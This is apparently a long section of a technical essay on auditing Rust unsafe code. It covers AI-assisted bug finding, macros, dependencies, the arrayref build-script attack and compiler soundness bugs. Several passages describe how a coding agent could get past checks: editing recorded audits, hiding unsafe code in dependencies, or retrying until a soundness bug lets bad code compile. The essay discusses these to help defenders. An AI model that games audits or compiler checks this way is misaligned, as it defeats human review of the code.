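An auditor does not need an elaborate system like MDASH. *The unreasonable effectiveness of LLMs for auditing Rust code* (Davidoff, 2026) describes auditing with just a prompt and OpenAI's coding tool Codex, running GPT-5.5. Davidoff, a lead of Rust's Secure Code Working Group, reported dozens of issues in widely used crates, none of them devastating.

The most serious bug was an out-of-bounds write in `jxl-grid`, part of a decoder for JPEG XL images. Davidoff had already fuzzed this crate without finding the bug, which occurs only on 32-bit machines with very large images. When Davidoff wrote in June, the Rust Foundation was about to report on its own audits with Anthropic's Claude Mythos.

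Anthropic's researchers had used an early version of that model, Mythos Preview, in much the same way. They gave it a one-paragraph prompt and ran many copies in parallel, each concentrating on a different file. Carlini, Cheng and colleagues (2026) report in *Assessing Claude Mythos Preview's cybersecurity capabilities* that the model found a fault in a virtual machine monitor, the program that keeps cloud customers apart when they share a computer. The monitor was written in a memory-safe language, but the fault was in an unsafe operation. It let a malicious customer write outside the permitted memory and easily crash the host. The model could not use the fault to take over the host. Carlini and colleagues did not name the project because its developers had not yet fixed the fault.

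These searches cost little compared with paying a person for the 19 weeks that an audit of Bun might take. A thousand runs on the operating system OpenBSD cost under $20,000 and produced several dozen findings.

### Removing false alarms

To avoid wasting maintainers' time, Davidoff required the model to write, for each suspected bug, a test that made Miri report undefined behaviour. If Miri found nothing wrong, Davidoff discarded the suspicion before anyone else saw it. AddressSanitizer, which detects many invalid memory accesses in a running program, can do a similar job for C and C++. Carlini and colleagues sent Firefox's developers 112 bugs found by an earlier model, Claude Opus 4.6. All of them were real, which the team credits to tools like AddressSanitizer.

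Davidoff's claim that Miri completely eliminates false positives is true only if the test uses the library properly. A test can contain unsafe code of its own that breaks a function's contract. If it sits inside the library's module, it can also set private fields, such as the four-byte buffer's `len`. Miri would then report undefined behaviour even though the library was sound. Somebody still has to check the test, although this is much quicker than auditing the library.

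Miri also enforces experimental rules about when two pointers may refer to the same memory. Davidoff had to switch to a newer version of these rules to avoid false alarms. Miri cannot run C code and supports only some requests to the operating system, so it cannot confirm many faults at the system boundary or in the calls to C and C++ that would make up most of Bun's remaining unsafe code. Davidoff uses sanitizers there instead, but they detect fewer kinds of fault.

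Microsoft has released less information about MDASH's false alarms. In one test, MDASH found all 21 flaws that Microsoft had planted in an unpublished driver and raised no false alarms. But iTnews' *Microsoft's MDASH AI vulnerability scanner finds four critical Windows RCEs* notes that Microsoft gave no false-positive rate for real code. Microsoft also did not say how many suspected faults it examined to find the 16 Windows vulnerabilities it announced.

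Even without false alarms, people remain the bottleneck. Anthropic pays security contractors to check every report before it goes to a maintainer. They agreed exactly with the model's severity rating in 89% of 198 reports. When Carlini and colleagues wrote, maintainers had fully patched fewer than 1% of the potential vulnerabilities, and the team said it might eventually have to relax its human review. Maintainers had acknowledged or patched only 29 of the 55 bugs CULPA found by the time of its paper.

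### What a clean audit is worth

Davidoff also audited `jxl-rs`, the JPEG XL decoder that Firefox and Chromium are adopting, and it "came up clean". How reassuring this is depends on the auditor's recall, the share of existing faults that it finds. Suppose a module has a probability *p* of containing a fault, and the auditor would find that fault with probability *r*. After a clean audit, the probability that the module contains a fault is

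$$\frac{p(1-r)}{p(1-r) + (1-p)}$$

InfoQ reports that MDASH found 96% of the historical vulnerabilities in one Windows component and all of those in another. A clean audit by a tool with 96% recall would reduce a 20% chance of a fault to about 1%. With Safe4U's 55% recall on published bugs, the chance would still be about 10%.

A 1% risk may be acceptable for one module, but the risks add up in a large program. If a program has 50 faults, an auditor with 96% recall will miss two on average. If the misses are independent, the chance of finding all 50 is only 13%. Fixing 48 faults is a big improvement, but the guarantee described at the start requires fixing every one.

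Actual recall is probably lower than these tests suggest. People have already found the historical bugs, and undiscovered ones may be harder to find. Carlini and colleagues also point out that a model may have memorized published bugs during training. Microsoft's planted flaws avoid that problem, but 21 is a small sample. A tool that misses one flaw in eight would still find all 21 about 6% of the time.

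Any clean audit may have missed bugs, even in old code. Mythos Preview found a 27-year-old bug in OpenBSD, which is known for its security, and a 16-year-old one in FFmpeg, an intensively fuzzed video library. Earlier audits that missed these bugs could have seemed reassuring.

In *Needle in the haystack*, devansh argues that long instructions and too many background documents are among the fastest ways to miss important vulnerabilities, because models become less reliable at picking out details as the text grows. Leaving material out can also hide a fault in unsafe code, since the line that reveals it may be in a distant function or a C library's manual.

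An AI system that reports a bug can stay outside the trusted base if it supplies a test that anyone can run to confirm the bug. A clean audit has no equivalent test, so if a team ships unsafe code because an AI system found nothing wrong with it, that system becomes part of the trusted base.

Asking the model to argue that the code is correct gives people more to check. Faisal (2026) reports in *Claude Found a Seven-Year Bug in the Rust Compiler* that this was one of the two best methods in a recent Anthropic study, because each failed argument pointed to a possible bug. A successful argument can still contain a mistake, so the standard-library project that Cook and colleagues describe uses verification tools to prove the absence of undefined behaviour.

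### When author and auditor make the same mistake

Suppose two reviewers each miss 10% of faults. If their misses are independent, 1% of faults get past both. If they miss exactly the same faults, 10% get past both, the same as with one reviewer.

This is a particular concern when the same model writes and audits the code. A model that wrongly believes a C library never returns a null pointer will write `readings` without a null check, and may later approve it for the same reason. The survey of engineers mentioned earlier found that many organisations have agents review their own code.

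Bun's translation suggests that review by agents that have not seen the author's reasoning helps, but not reliably. The reviewing agents caught the use-after-free involving a pipe but let `PathString` through. A second review also needs to cover files where the first found nothing. Carlini and colleagues had another copy of Mythos Preview re-examine each bug report, which removed unimportant ones, but that copy did not recheck such files, so it could not find bugs missed there.

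The usual answer is to vary the auditors. MDASH combines several models and gives its agents different jobs. A team can also vary the prompts, for instance by hiding the `SAFETY` comments from one auditor. Tools that work completely differently should help most. Miri runs the code, so the author's beliefs about the code don't affect its results. In `jxl-grid`, a language model found what a fuzzer had missed, and the reverse could easily happen on other code.

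How much it helps in practice to use a variety of auditing tools is unclear. CULPA found every bug that the other five tools in its comparison found, so running them as well would have added nothing. But 55 of the 119 bugs were included only because CULPA had found them, which makes the comparison a weak test of what CULPA misses. It missed four of the published bugs, one because it occurs only on a particular platform and another because CULPA had no rule for an experimental function. A language model reading the source might have caught either of those two.

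Using a variety of auditors can't compensate for an error in a source they all use. Different companies' models learn from much of the same public code and documentation, and CULPA's rules come from that documentation too. If a safety contract omits a condition, as some in the standard library have, all of these auditors may miss it.

Varying the auditors also helps less against an author that optimises to pass the audit, since it may learn to satisfy all of them at once. A developer who trains a model against a group of auditors could keep one out of the training and use it only on the finished code. But if the developer then keeps revising the code until that auditor approves it, the auditor is no longer an independent check.

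## How does unsafe code enter through macros, dependencies and build scripts?

An auditor usually starts by searching a team's source files for `unsafe`, but this search misses code generated by macros and code from dependencies, both of which end up in the finished Rust program. Some dependencies also include programs that run on the developer's machine during the build, and these can do harm without any unsafe code.

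### Macros that write unsafe code for their callers

The compiler replaces each use of a macro with the code the macro generates, a step called expansion. If that code includes an unsafe block, the caller's crate now has an unsafe block that nobody typed there. This is harmless if the macro also generates the checks the block relies on, just as a sound function would perform them.

A badly built macro can also run the caller's own code inside its unsafe block. This invented macro returns the first byte of a slice:

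```rust
macro_rules! first {
    ($slice:expr) => {
        unsafe {
            let s: &[u8] = $slice;
            assert!(!s.is_empty());
            *s.get_unchecked(0)
        }
    };
}
```

Expansion replaces `$slice` with whatever expression the caller supplies. The unsafe block is there for `get_unchecked`, and the `assert!` line makes that call safe by stopping the program if the slice is empty. But the caller's expression ends up inside the block too, so the compiler accepts this function:

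```rust
pub fn peek(p: *const u8) -> u8 {
    first!(std::slice::from_raw_parts(p, 4))
}
```

`from_raw_parts` is the unsafe function from the `Sensor` example, and here the macro supplies the unsafe block it requires. `peek` looks like safe code, but passing it a null pointer causes undefined behaviour. The programmer who wrote `peek` never typed `unsafe`, so no rule about `SAFETY` comments applied.

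To fix the macro, its author moves the `let` line above the unsafe block. The compiler then treats the caller's expression as ordinary code and rejects `peek`. Clippy has a lint for this mistake, but its documentation in Rust's source code describes two gaps. The lint checks macros only where they are expanded, so it misses any that the crate defines but never uses. By default it also ignores the crate's private macros, because most warnings about them would be noise.

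Macros may account for a large share of unsafe code. *Unsafe in Rust*, an early survey of 3,638 crates, attributed 47% of unsafe operations to macros, including 32% to macros from other crates. Both figures are too high because the method attributed expressions that programmers typed inside `println!` to the macro. The figures also exclude 12,058 unsafe operations from Rust's built-in `derive` feature, which generates standard functions such as comparisons.

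### What `forbid(unsafe_code)` stops

The line `#![forbid(unsafe_code)]` helps a team keep its unsafe code in one layer. It sets the compiler's built-in `unsafe_code` lint to `forbid`, the strictest level. The next strictest level, `deny`, also makes unsafe code an error, but any part of the crate can permit it again. Rust's *Lint Levels* explains that nothing in the source can relax `forbid`.

| Where the unsafe code comes from | Effect of `forbid(unsafe_code)` |
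|---|---|
| A block, function or implementation written in the crate | Compiler rejects it |
| An unsafe attribute, such as `no_mangle` | Compiler rejects it |
| A macro defined in the same crate | Compiler rejects it |
| A macro defined in another crate | Compiler usually accepts it |
| A dependency | Compiler accepts it |

Before Rust 1.98, the `unsafe_code` lint missed some unsafe attributes. Rust's documentation lists only `no_mangle`, `export_name` and `link_section` under this lint, and developers had to add any others by hand. Nobody had added `naked`, which lets a programmer write a function's whole body in assembly language. *Move logic for emitting UNSAFE_CODE for unsafe attributes to attr parsing* (JonathanBrouwer, 2026) extended the lint to every unsafe attribute.

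The exception for other crates' macros is deliberate. japaric (2018), in *#[deny] in expansion of proc macro is ignored*, reported that the compiler had stopped applying most lints to code from such macros. A compiler developer replied that programmers can probably do nothing about code that somebody else's macro generates. japaric partly welcomed the change because macro authors no longer had to add lines everywhere to permit unsafe code and avoid breaking the builds of users who had banned it.

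The exception isn't completely reliable. *forbid means forbid, until linkme needs a word* describes a project that forbids unsafe code in its production crates but uses `linkme`, whose macro generates a `link_section` attribute. The compiler rejected the files that used the macro, so the developer had to permit unsafe code in them. This is possibly because the compiler determines where code came from by its source location, and a macro can give the code it generates its caller's location.

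The compiler also has an attribute, `allow_internal_unsafe`, that lets a macro use unsafe code without triggering the `unsafe_code` lint where the macro is called. One of Rust's own tests gives this attribute to a macro named `evil!` and uses the macro to read from a null pointer. Under `forbid(unsafe_code)`, the compiler rejects the attribute but only warns about the null pointer.

A crate's `#![forbid(unsafe_code)]` line also has no effect on its dependencies, and a dependency's own `forbid` line has no effect when somebody else builds it. Cargo, Rust's standard build tool, runs the compiler with lints silenced for dependencies. According to *RFC 1193*, which proposed this, the compiler then ignores even `forbid`. This keeps a dependency's warnings out of the build output and prevents a stricter lint in a new compiler from breaking the build. But a crate could then declare `#![forbid(unsafe_code)]`,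 contain an unsafe block, and still compile for everyone who depends on it.

### One program, four counts

Counting tools disagree partly because they examine the same program at different stages. The simplest method is a text search of the source files. Fuchsia's *Rust Unsafe Analyzer* parses each file into a syntax tree, a structured form of the code, and reports every `unsafe` keyword it finds there. *cargo-geiger* also parses source files, but includes those of the program's dependencies. `cargo-expand` prints the code after macro expansion, so an auditor can count the `unsafe` code that macros generated.

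Here is the repaired macro, with a function that uses it three times:

```rust
macro_rules! first {
    ($slice:expr) => {{
        let s: &[u8] = $slice;
        assert!(!s.is_empty());
        unsafe { *s.get_unchecked(0) }
    }};
}

// No unsafe code here, only uses of `first`.
pub fn initials(a: &[u8], b: &[u8], c: &[u8]) -> [u8; 3] {
    [first!(a), first!(b), first!(c)]
}
```

The second column below gives the count for this file. The third gives the count if the team moves `first` to another crate and leaves `initials` where it is.

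| Method | `first` in this file | `first` in another crate |
|---|---|---|
| Text search for `unsafe` | 2 | 1 |
| Fuchsia's analyser | 1 | 0 |
| cargo-geiger | 0 | 0 |
| Unsafe blocks after expansion | 3 | 3 |

The text search counts the comment, and after the move it finds nothing else. Fuchsia's analyser ignores comments and has a special rule for macro definitions that contain `unsafe`, but it cannot detect unsafe code generated by a macro from elsewhere. cargo-geiger does not examine the insides of macros. Only the last method finds the unsafe code in `initials`, although it counts one line three times. An auditor could use expansion to find which macros generate unsafe code, then read each of those macros once.

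cargo-geiger counts unsafe functions and expressions separately, so its totals are not comparable with a count of unsafe blocks, such as the one in Bun's audit. It also gives two numbers for each crate, one for unsafe code in files the build used and one for all the unsafe code found in the crate. According to its changelog, it leaves out tests unless the user asks for them.

Fuchsia uses its analyser to decide which changes need a specialist's review, but the tool reports an unsafe block only if the change adds or modifies the line with the `unsafe` keyword. If an AI agent altered a pointer calculation on a later line of the same block, the tool would not flag the change for review.

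### Unsafe code in dependencies

*Is Rust Used Safely by Software Developers?* (Evans, Campbell and Soffa, 2020) analysed over 85% of the valid public Rust libraries then available and found that about half either used unsafe code or depended on a library that did. Only 29% contained the keyword `unsafe` themselves, so a search of each library's own files would have missed over a third of those affected. About 60% of the most downloaded libraries included unsafe code. These figures are now old, but the earlier *Unsafe in Rust* also found unsafe code in 29% of libraries, so the direct share may be fairly stable.

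Evans and colleagues conclude that most crates lack a compiler guarantee of memory safety, which is strictly true but makes the situation sound worse than it is. Safe code can rely on a sound library, as the RustBelt proof shows for its model of Rust. The 50% figure is therefore better understood as the share of crates whose safety depends on a person having judged some unsafe code correctly. Heavy use of a few popular crates could even help, since one careful audit would serve everyone who depends on them.

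The amount of code is a bigger problem. Servo, a web browser engine, consisted of about 50 crates, but compiling it meant compiling almost 400. If Servo's team had audited only its own crates, it would have skipped about seven-eighths of the crates it compiled.

Some of this code isn't Rust. Evans and colleagues found that 22% of the unsafe functions that crates called were in C libraries. C has no `unsafe` keyword, so all four methods above would count zero in a C library of any size. But a stray write in that library can corrupt the Rust program's memory, so the whole library is part of the trusted base.

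A search can find only the Rust code that declares or calls the C functions, and the calls may not be marked `unsafe`. *3484 unsafe extern blocks*, the proposal behind the `unsafe extern` rule described earlier, also lets programmers declare individual C functions as safe to call. This is reasonable for a mathematical function that accepts any number, and it removes pointless unsafe blocks. But `unsafe` then appears only on the `extern` block that declares the function. Fuchsia's analyser flags the unsafe blocks that call C functions but not the `extern` blocks that declare them, so it could miss a function declared this way.

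### Programs that run during the build

A crate can include a build script, a Rust program in a file named `build.rs` that Cargo compiles and runs before it compiles the crate. Build scripts have ordinary uses, such as finding a C library or checking which features the compiler supports. A crate can also define procedural macros, which are Rust functions that the compiler runs to generate code. (The `first` macro is of a simpler kind that only fills in a template.)

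Build scripts and procedural macros run on the machine that builds the program, before anyone can inspect or test the result. A build script has all the privileges of the user who started the build, which on a developer's machine often include access to passwords and signing keys. Benamou (2026), in *Compromised Rust crates on crates.io silently execute malware at build time*, points out that build scripts run even without a full build, such as during `cargo check`, which only looks for errors, and when a code editor analyses the project in the background. Using `cargo-expand` on a suspicious crate also runs its scripts, so an auditor should use it on an isolated machine.

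### The arrayref attack

On 20 August 2026, an attacker used a build script to spread malware through `arrayref`, a tiny crate of macros for handling arrays. The crate had about 245 million downloads, mostly because other crates depend on it. *Rust Supply Chain Attack on arrayref* (McCarthy and Read, 2026) reports that `arrayref` was found in three-quarters of the computing environments that contain any Rust.

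Likhith (2026), in *Rust Supply-Chain Attack*, reconstructed the sequence from the logs of crates.io, Rust's public registry of crates. All times are in UTC.

1. At 01:25, the attacker opened an account called `dtolney`. David Tolnay, who wrote several of Rust's most widely used crates, is `dtolnay`.
2. At 01:55, this account published `proc-macro1`, a clean copy of Tolnay's crate `proc-macro2`. The harmless release gave the new crate a history.
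3. At 07:11, the attacker published a new version of `proc-macro1` with a malicious build script.
4. At 07:15, the attacker used the account of arrayref's real owner to publish arrayref 0.3.10, which depended on `proc-macro1`. In ten years, arrayref had never had a dependency.
5. Over the next 40 seconds, the attacker "yanked" five older versions of arrayref, which marks them as withdrawn.

The last step exploited a safety feature, Cargo's warning about yanked versions. Yanking a version does not break existing projects, but Cargo warns their developers to consider updating to one that isn't yanked. The newest unyanked version was the malicious one, and the person who reported the attack to RustSec had installed it by following this advice.

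The build script downloaded a program from the attacker's server, saved it to disk and started it in the background. Safe Rust allows all three operations, so the script needed no unsafe block. The rest of `proc-macro1` was genuine code, so builds succeeded and tests passed. In arrayref, the attacker had changed only the list of dependencies. An auditor comparing the source code of the two versions would have found no difference, and a count of unsafe code would not have changed.

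Goregaokar (2026), in *Supply chain attack on arrayref*, writes for Rust's security team that the arrayref owner's computer or credentials were probably compromised. The team removed the malicious version after 86 minutes, along with releases of two other crates by the same owner. RustSec's *arrayref 0.3.10 was removed from crates.io due to a malicious dependency* (2026) counts 2,285 downloads of that version, less than 10% of arrayref's downloads in that period. Most projects stayed on an older release because they had a lockfile, which records the exact version of each dependency.

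The full damage is unknown. Benamou could not retrieve the downloaded program because the server had stopped responding. One infected developer reported that the program installed a service to restart itself. McCarthy and Read found that the attacker's servers overlapped with those used in earlier North Korean campaigns.

The attack did not make any finished program memory-unsafe, so in one sense it falls outside Rust's guarantee. But a program running with the developer's privileges could also edit the source code after review or replace the compiler. Everything that runs during the build therefore belongs to the trusted base, even for a team that cares only about memory safety.

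A build script can also do damage without downloading anything. Aikido's *compromised rust crate onering performs code exfiltration* describes one in the onering crate that collected the source code of the latest commit from any project that built the crate and sent it to a remote server. The crate's public repository also appeared to be compromised, so developers could not avoid the problem by getting the code there instead of from crates.io.

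### Recording audits and sharing them

A small team cannot read 400 crates, but many teams use the same ones and can divide the work. *Static Analysis and Auditing*, a chapter of a guide to secure Rust, describes two tools for this. `cargo vet` checks that somebody has recorded an audit for every dependency. Each record names the auditor, the exact version, and the standard the crate met, such as `safe-to-deploy`. With `cargo-crev`, reviewers publish their findings, and each user decides which reviewers to trust. Google also grades crates in its audits by their risk of undefined behaviour, so a team can require a better grade for code that handles untrusted files than for an internal tool.

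`cargo vet` could have stopped the arrayref attack if it had run before any of the new code did. The check would have failed because an audit of version 0.3.9 does not cover 0.3.10, and nobody would have recorded an audit of `proc-macro1`. But if a developer updates the lockfile with an editor open, the editor may run the new build scripts before the developer runs `cargo vet`. A team that accepts whatever a known maintainer publishes, without auditing each version, would have had no protection, because the bad release came from the real owner's account.

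The standard that the auditor applies matters as well. Someone who assessed only the risk of undefined behaviour could have given `proc-macro1` a good grade, since the malicious script contained no unsafe code. An audit meant to prevent such attacks has to cover build scripts and procedural macros in full, and ask what each one reads, writes and contacts. (Tools that flag file and network access can help with this.)

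The main burden is that each new version needs another audit. Suppose a project the size of Servo has 350 outside crates and each releases four versions a year. The team and its partners would have to approve 1,400 new versions a year, or about 27 a week. Reading only the changes makes this much more manageable. For arrayref 0.3.10, the change was a single new dependency, and a reviewer would have had good reason to wonder why such a small crate needed one. But the new dependency has no earlier audited version to compare with, so someone has to read all of it.

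An easier precaution is to wait a few days before adopting any new version. Malicious releases are often removed sooner than that, and the three in August were online for less than two hours each. Benamou's employer, JFrog, sells a product that enforces such a delay, and says its users were fully protected. Waiting also delays fixes for real vulnerabilities, unless someone makes an exception for them, and it relies on someone else examining the new release in the meantime, perhaps with an automated scanner.

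A team can also restrict which servers a build can contact. Likhith's company, StepSecurity, sells a tool that monitors network connections on build servers. When Likhith rebuilt a project with the malicious arrayref, the build succeeded, and the only visible sign of trouble was a connection to an unfamiliar address. After the company blocked that address, the script could not download its program. Allowing builds to contact only a short list of approved servers would have stopped the download even if nobody knew the address in advance.

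### When an AI agent picks the dependencies

An AI agent can add a crate by writing one line in a project's configuration file, and it will usually then compile the project to check that the change works. Compiling runs any build scripts in the new crate and all its dependencies, with the same access the agent has. A person who reviews the pull request afterwards is too late to prevent any harm those scripts did.

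The arrayref attack would probably have worked well on agents, because Cargo's warning recommended an update and an agent told to clear all warnings has good reason to install it. Attackers can also exploit wrong crate names. `proc-macro1` differs from the real crate's name by one character, and a language model that writes a plausible but wrong name may install whatever an attacker has registered under it.

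Dependencies also give an agent a way to reduce the unsafe code in its own work without making the program safer. Suppose a team requires `forbid(unsafe_code)` and the agent needs to skip a bounds check. It could find a crate that offers the operation as a safe function, or a macro that generates the unsafe block, and the compiler would accept the result. If the function is unsound, the program has the same fault as if the agent had written the unsafe code itself, but in a place where the team is less likely to look.

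The simplest defence is to run agents on isolated machines that hold no passwords or signing keys, and to let them use only crates the team has already approved. A person can then decide whether to allow each new crate before anything compiles it. If the team uses `cargo vet`, the agent must not be able to edit the file of recorded audits, or it could approve its own choices to make the check pass.

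Agents might also reduce the number of dependencies. People often add tiny crates to avoid writing a few dozen lines, and an agent can write those lines in seconds. That would remove the risk from a stranger's account and build script. But the team would be replacing code that thousands of others had used, and some had audited, with its own private version, so this makes much more sense for a simple text function than for anything that needs unsafe code.

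## Can code without the unsafe mark still break memory safety?

Safe code can break memory safety because the compiler has faults of its own. Both `forbid(unsafe_code)` and a search for `unsafe` rely on the compiler to reject every dangerous program that lacks the mark, so the compiler belongs to the trusted base of every Rust program. A dangerous program can get past it in three ways:

- The type checker, which here means all the compiler's rule checks including the borrow checker, accepts a program that breaks the rules. Such a flaw is a soundness bug in the compiler.
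- The optimiser, which rewrites accepted code to make it faster, turns a correct program into a faulty one. This is a miscompilation.
- The operating system offers the program another route to its own memory. On Linux, a special file represents each running program's memory. Writing to a file is an ordinary safe operation in Rust, so a program could overwrite its own data this way without any unsafe code.

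The Rust project doesn't count access through this file as a bug in the language. It treats the file as outside the program, like a debugger, and leaves it to a sandbox to block access. Honest programmers rarely have a reason to open the file. An auditor can search the code for its name, but the search can miss a name that the program assembles while it runs.

Mistakes in the standard library's unsafe code can also let safe code cause undefined behaviour, as Bae found, but in those cases the auditor has an unsafe block to examine.

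### Safe code that reads freed memory

In August 2026, Anthropic's researchers reported that their AI model Claude had found a five-line program, written entirely in safe code, that reads freed memory. The program starts to borrow an item from a nested array, then frees part of the array before it has determined which item to borrow. The borrow checker fails to connect the two steps. According to Faisal, Rust's contributors traced the flaw to an experimental compiler version of 23 April 2019, which switched on a new method of tracking how long references last. The flaw was still open on 3 December 2026.

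On 13 October, *struct's lifetime requirements can be bypassed via covariant field assignment* (jsnell) reported an older flaw, a missing check in the compiler. A Rust type can require that any reference stored in it stay valid for as long as the program runs. The compiler did not always enforce this requirement when a program put something into an existing value. Code that runs when the value is destroyed may rely on the requirement, and can keep a reference to memory the program is about to free. Owen (2026) reports in *What the 11-year-old Rust borrow checker bug means* that contributors reproduced the flaw in compiler versions going back 11 years. One of them triggered it through a different language feature, so a repair may have to cover more than the reported case.

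Faisal reports that about 178 soundness issues were open in December 2026. *Mitigating Bugs in the Linux eBPF Verifier* (Gerhorst and Hönig, 2025) gives a count of 94 from February 2025. The rise doesn't show that the compiler is getting worse, because the two counts may not cover exactly the same kinds of issue, and people and AI systems are now searching harder.

Ordinary testing is bad at finding these flaws. *An Empirical Study of Rust-Specific Bugs in the rustc Compiler* (Liu, Feng and colleagues, 2025) examined 301 confirmed bugs from 2022 to 2024 in the parts of the compiler that handle Rust's distinctive features. In about 26% of them, the compiler accepted an invalid program or rejected a valid one. Only the first error threatens safety. Existing testing tools had detected just 6% of the bugs that didn't crash the compiler. Many of these tools generate random programs and look for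 crashes, so they miss the error when the compiler accepts an invalid program and finishes normally.

### Anthropic's search for logic bugs

A flaw of this kind is a logic bug, in which software breaks a rule about what it is meant to do without crashing or corrupting its own memory. Anthropic's *Finding logic bugs without general-purpose bug oracles* (2026) compares four ways of using language models to find such bugs:

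- **Agentic code review:** the model reads the source code, guesses where a rule might fail and tests the guesses.
- **Informal correctness proofs:** the model looks for bugs by trying to argue that the code is correct.
- **Fuzzing:** a fuzzer generates the inputs, and the model supplies checks that should flag wrong results.
- **Symbolic execution:** an analysis engine treats the inputs as unknowns, as in algebra, and works out which values would lead the code down each path.

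The researchers tested the methods on 21 logic bugs that developers had already fixed: nine in the database SQLite, eight in the image library image-png, and four in the compression tools zstd and Brotli (Pogorelec, 2026, *Anthropic's AI bug tests uncover previously undisclosed flaws*). The model, Claude Mythos 5, received the unfixed code and had three attempts at each bug. It succeeded if it produced an input on which the fixed and unfixed versions gave different results. In half the trials, the researchers also told it which rule the code broke.

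| Method | Bugs found from the code alone | Bugs found when told the rule |
|---|---|---|
| Agentic code review | 11 | 20 |
| Informal correctness proofs | 8 | 21 |
| Symbolic execution | 0 | 13 |
| Fuzzing | 0 | 1 |

Even the score of 13 for symbolic execution overstates the method's contribution, because the model found those bugs by reading the code and the engine confirmed only two. Stating the rule had a larger effect, raising the score for proofs from 8 to 21. Most software has no complete written list of its rules, and neither does Rust's type system.

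The benchmark is small and contains no compiler bugs. In code review without hints, Claude Sonnet 4.5 found one bug and Claude Mythos 5.2 found 15. Antipov (2026), in *Linux, к твоему контролёру есть вопросы*, adds that newer models remember some of the old bugs. This may explain part of the progress between models.

Memorization can't explain the discovery of unknown bugs, though. When the researchers asked Claude to prove that safe Rust is type-safe, the failed proofs led to several dozen type-safety problems, including the flaw from 2019. Rust's developers have already fixed some of them. Nicholas Carlini, one of the researchers, is not a Rust expert, so he had developers who know the language check the 2019 flaw before he reported it. Other candidates still need this check, so the final number could change.

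### A checker for programs that nobody trusts

The same proof method found more than 100 soundness bugs in the verifier, a checker inside the Linux kernel. Linux lets users load small programs, written for a system called eBPF, into the running kernel for jobs such as filtering network traffic. These programs run with the kernel's privileges, so the verifier must examine each one first and reject any that could misuse memory.

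In one of the bugs, which dated from 2020, the verifier applied a rule about pointers that can never be null (zero) to a comparison that checked only 32 bits. Pointers on most modern computers have 64 bits, and the 32 bits checked can all be zero even when the full pointer is not. The verifier therefore approved programs that could read memory unsafely, and a user with an account on the machine could gain higher privileges. Antipov reports that the kernel's developers have received all the findings and have been releasing fixes for months.

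The eBPF verifier is a useful comparison for Rust because its designers expected hostile authors. Its job is also much simpler than the Rust compiler's, since eBPF programs are small and restricted. If it still had over 100 soundness bugs after years of attention from attackers and researchers, we should not assume that nearly all the flaws in Rust's compiler are known.

Some systems use Rust's compiler as a verifier. They load Rust code supplied by their users, such as kernel modules and cloud functions, and rely on the language and compiler to protect the rest of the system from it (Tiffany, Agvanian and colleagues, 2026). Asterinas also relies on the compiler to separate its two layers, so a soundness bug could let a driver written entirely in safe code overwrite any of the kernel's memory.

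### When the optimiser is wrong

After Rust's compiler has checked a program, it passes the program to LLVM, a set of compiler components that many other languages also use, for much of the optimisation. Rust's own tests include a known miscompilation of a program that has no unsafe code and breaks no rule. The optimised version treats the same number as zero in one place and non-zero in another, which can make the program crash.

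In May 2026, compiler engineer Justin Lebar had up to 50 AI agents at a time read LLVM's source code. Lebar (2026), in *Finding Miscompiles for Fun, Not Profit*, reports spending more than $10,000 in an afternoon and getting hundreds of plausible bugs. In the part of LLVM that produces code for ordinary Intel and AMD processors, the agents reported almost two a minute. Some reports were wrong and many concerned minor faults. But of the 30 or so that Lebar had examined, one was alarming because it showed that LLVM could split a write to memory that other threads must see as a single step into two separate writes. A thread that read the value between them would get half of the old value and half of the new one. Programs use such writes to coordinate threads, and the fault might appear so rarely that nobody could trace the resulting damage.

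This does not make LLVM unusually unreliable. Regehr and Livinskii wrote in an older article, *Looking for Missed Alarm Bugs in a Formal Verification Tool*, that the vast majority of its optimisations are correct. They work with Alive2, a tool that compares a function before and after an optimisation and tries to prove that the change was correct. Alive2 can miss errors, so they had to test it too.

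A miscompilation also poses a different problem for auditors than a soundness bug does. The source is correct, so even reading every line would not reveal the error, and auditors lose nothing here by reading only the unsafe code.

### Honest mistakes rarely hit these flaws

If the author makes only honest mistakes, unsafe code is a far greater danger than bugs in the compiler. Rust's *Project Zero*, a plan to fix every known soundness bug in the type system, describes these bugs as obscure and says they have "rarely if ever affected production systems". In a note on the October flaw, quoted by Owen, the project argues that a bug nobody noticed for 11 years "cannot actually be that easy to hit". The project gave the flaw high priority but not the highest.

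Mistakes in unsafe code are common. Chen and colleagues took 64 memory-safety bugs from recent RustSec advisories, and all of them violated a documented condition of an unsafe operation. If one in twenty such bugs came from the compiler, a sample of 64 would have only about a 4% chance of containing none. The sample is somewhat biased, since RustSec mostly lists faults in crates and a compiler fault would go to a different list. Still, the difference between unsafe-code mistakes and compiler flaws is large enough to support a commenter in *Soundness Concern*, a discussion on Rust's user forum, who called the focus on compiler flaws misdirected and named dependencies with unsafe code or C code as larger worries.

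There are two reasons for some caution. A program that reads freed memory may appear to work, so a lack of reports doesn't prove a flaw has done no harm. The 11 years of experience also come mostly from human-written code. AI systems may combine language features in ways people seldom do, and they write so much code that a rare accident is more likely to happen. Neither reason is likely to close the gap, so a team with honest authors should still spend its reading time on unsafe code.

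### An author that keeps trying

Ordinary code rarely hits a soundness bug, but that is much less reassuring if the author optimises against the check. If one attempt in a million hits such a bug, a million independent attempts by agents have a 63% chance of hitting at least one.

Those attempts would not be random either. Suppose an agent needs to keep a reference for longer than its data will last. The compiler correctly rejects the code, and the agent tries variations until the error disappears. A correct redesign would remove the error, but so would a variation that hits a soundness bug. The compiler rejects the other attempts that would break memory safety, so any that compile do so because of such a bug.

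According to the Rust project's note on the October flaw, exploiting it takes "an intentionally malicious" piece of code. That is a fair assumption about human programmers, who would have no other reason to write such code, but an agent could arrive at similar code just by trying to satisfy the compiler.

An author may not need to search for a soundness bug, because Rust's developers discuss open ones in public, usually with a short example program. This helps people fix the bugs, but a language model may have learned the examples during training or may find them online. *Project Zero* predicts that one of the known bugs, if left unfixed, is likely to become the basis for an exploit. Training can also make a rare trick common. If a developer rewards a model for code that compiles and passes its tests, one lucky success with the trick makes the model more likely to use it again.

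### Repairing the type checker

Many soundness bugs stay open because a simple fix would also make the compiler reject a lot of valid code. To fix them properly, Rust's developers first have to rebuild parts of the type checker. The most important part is the trait solver, which works out which function to call when several types provide their own version (Alden, 2026, *Rust's next-generation trait solver*). The new solver should fix some soundness bugs directly and make it possible to fix others.

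After nearly four years of work, the Rust project turned on its next-generation trait solver by default in the compiler's nightly test version on 21 August 2026. In *Enabling the next-generation trait solver on nightly*, lcnr (2026) calls this the largest single change to the compiler since its first release and expects it to reach the stable version within months. The project is also testing a new borrow checker, partly to find soundness problems that its designers had not thought of (Rust Blog, *Enabling the next iteration of the borrow checker on nightly*, 2026).

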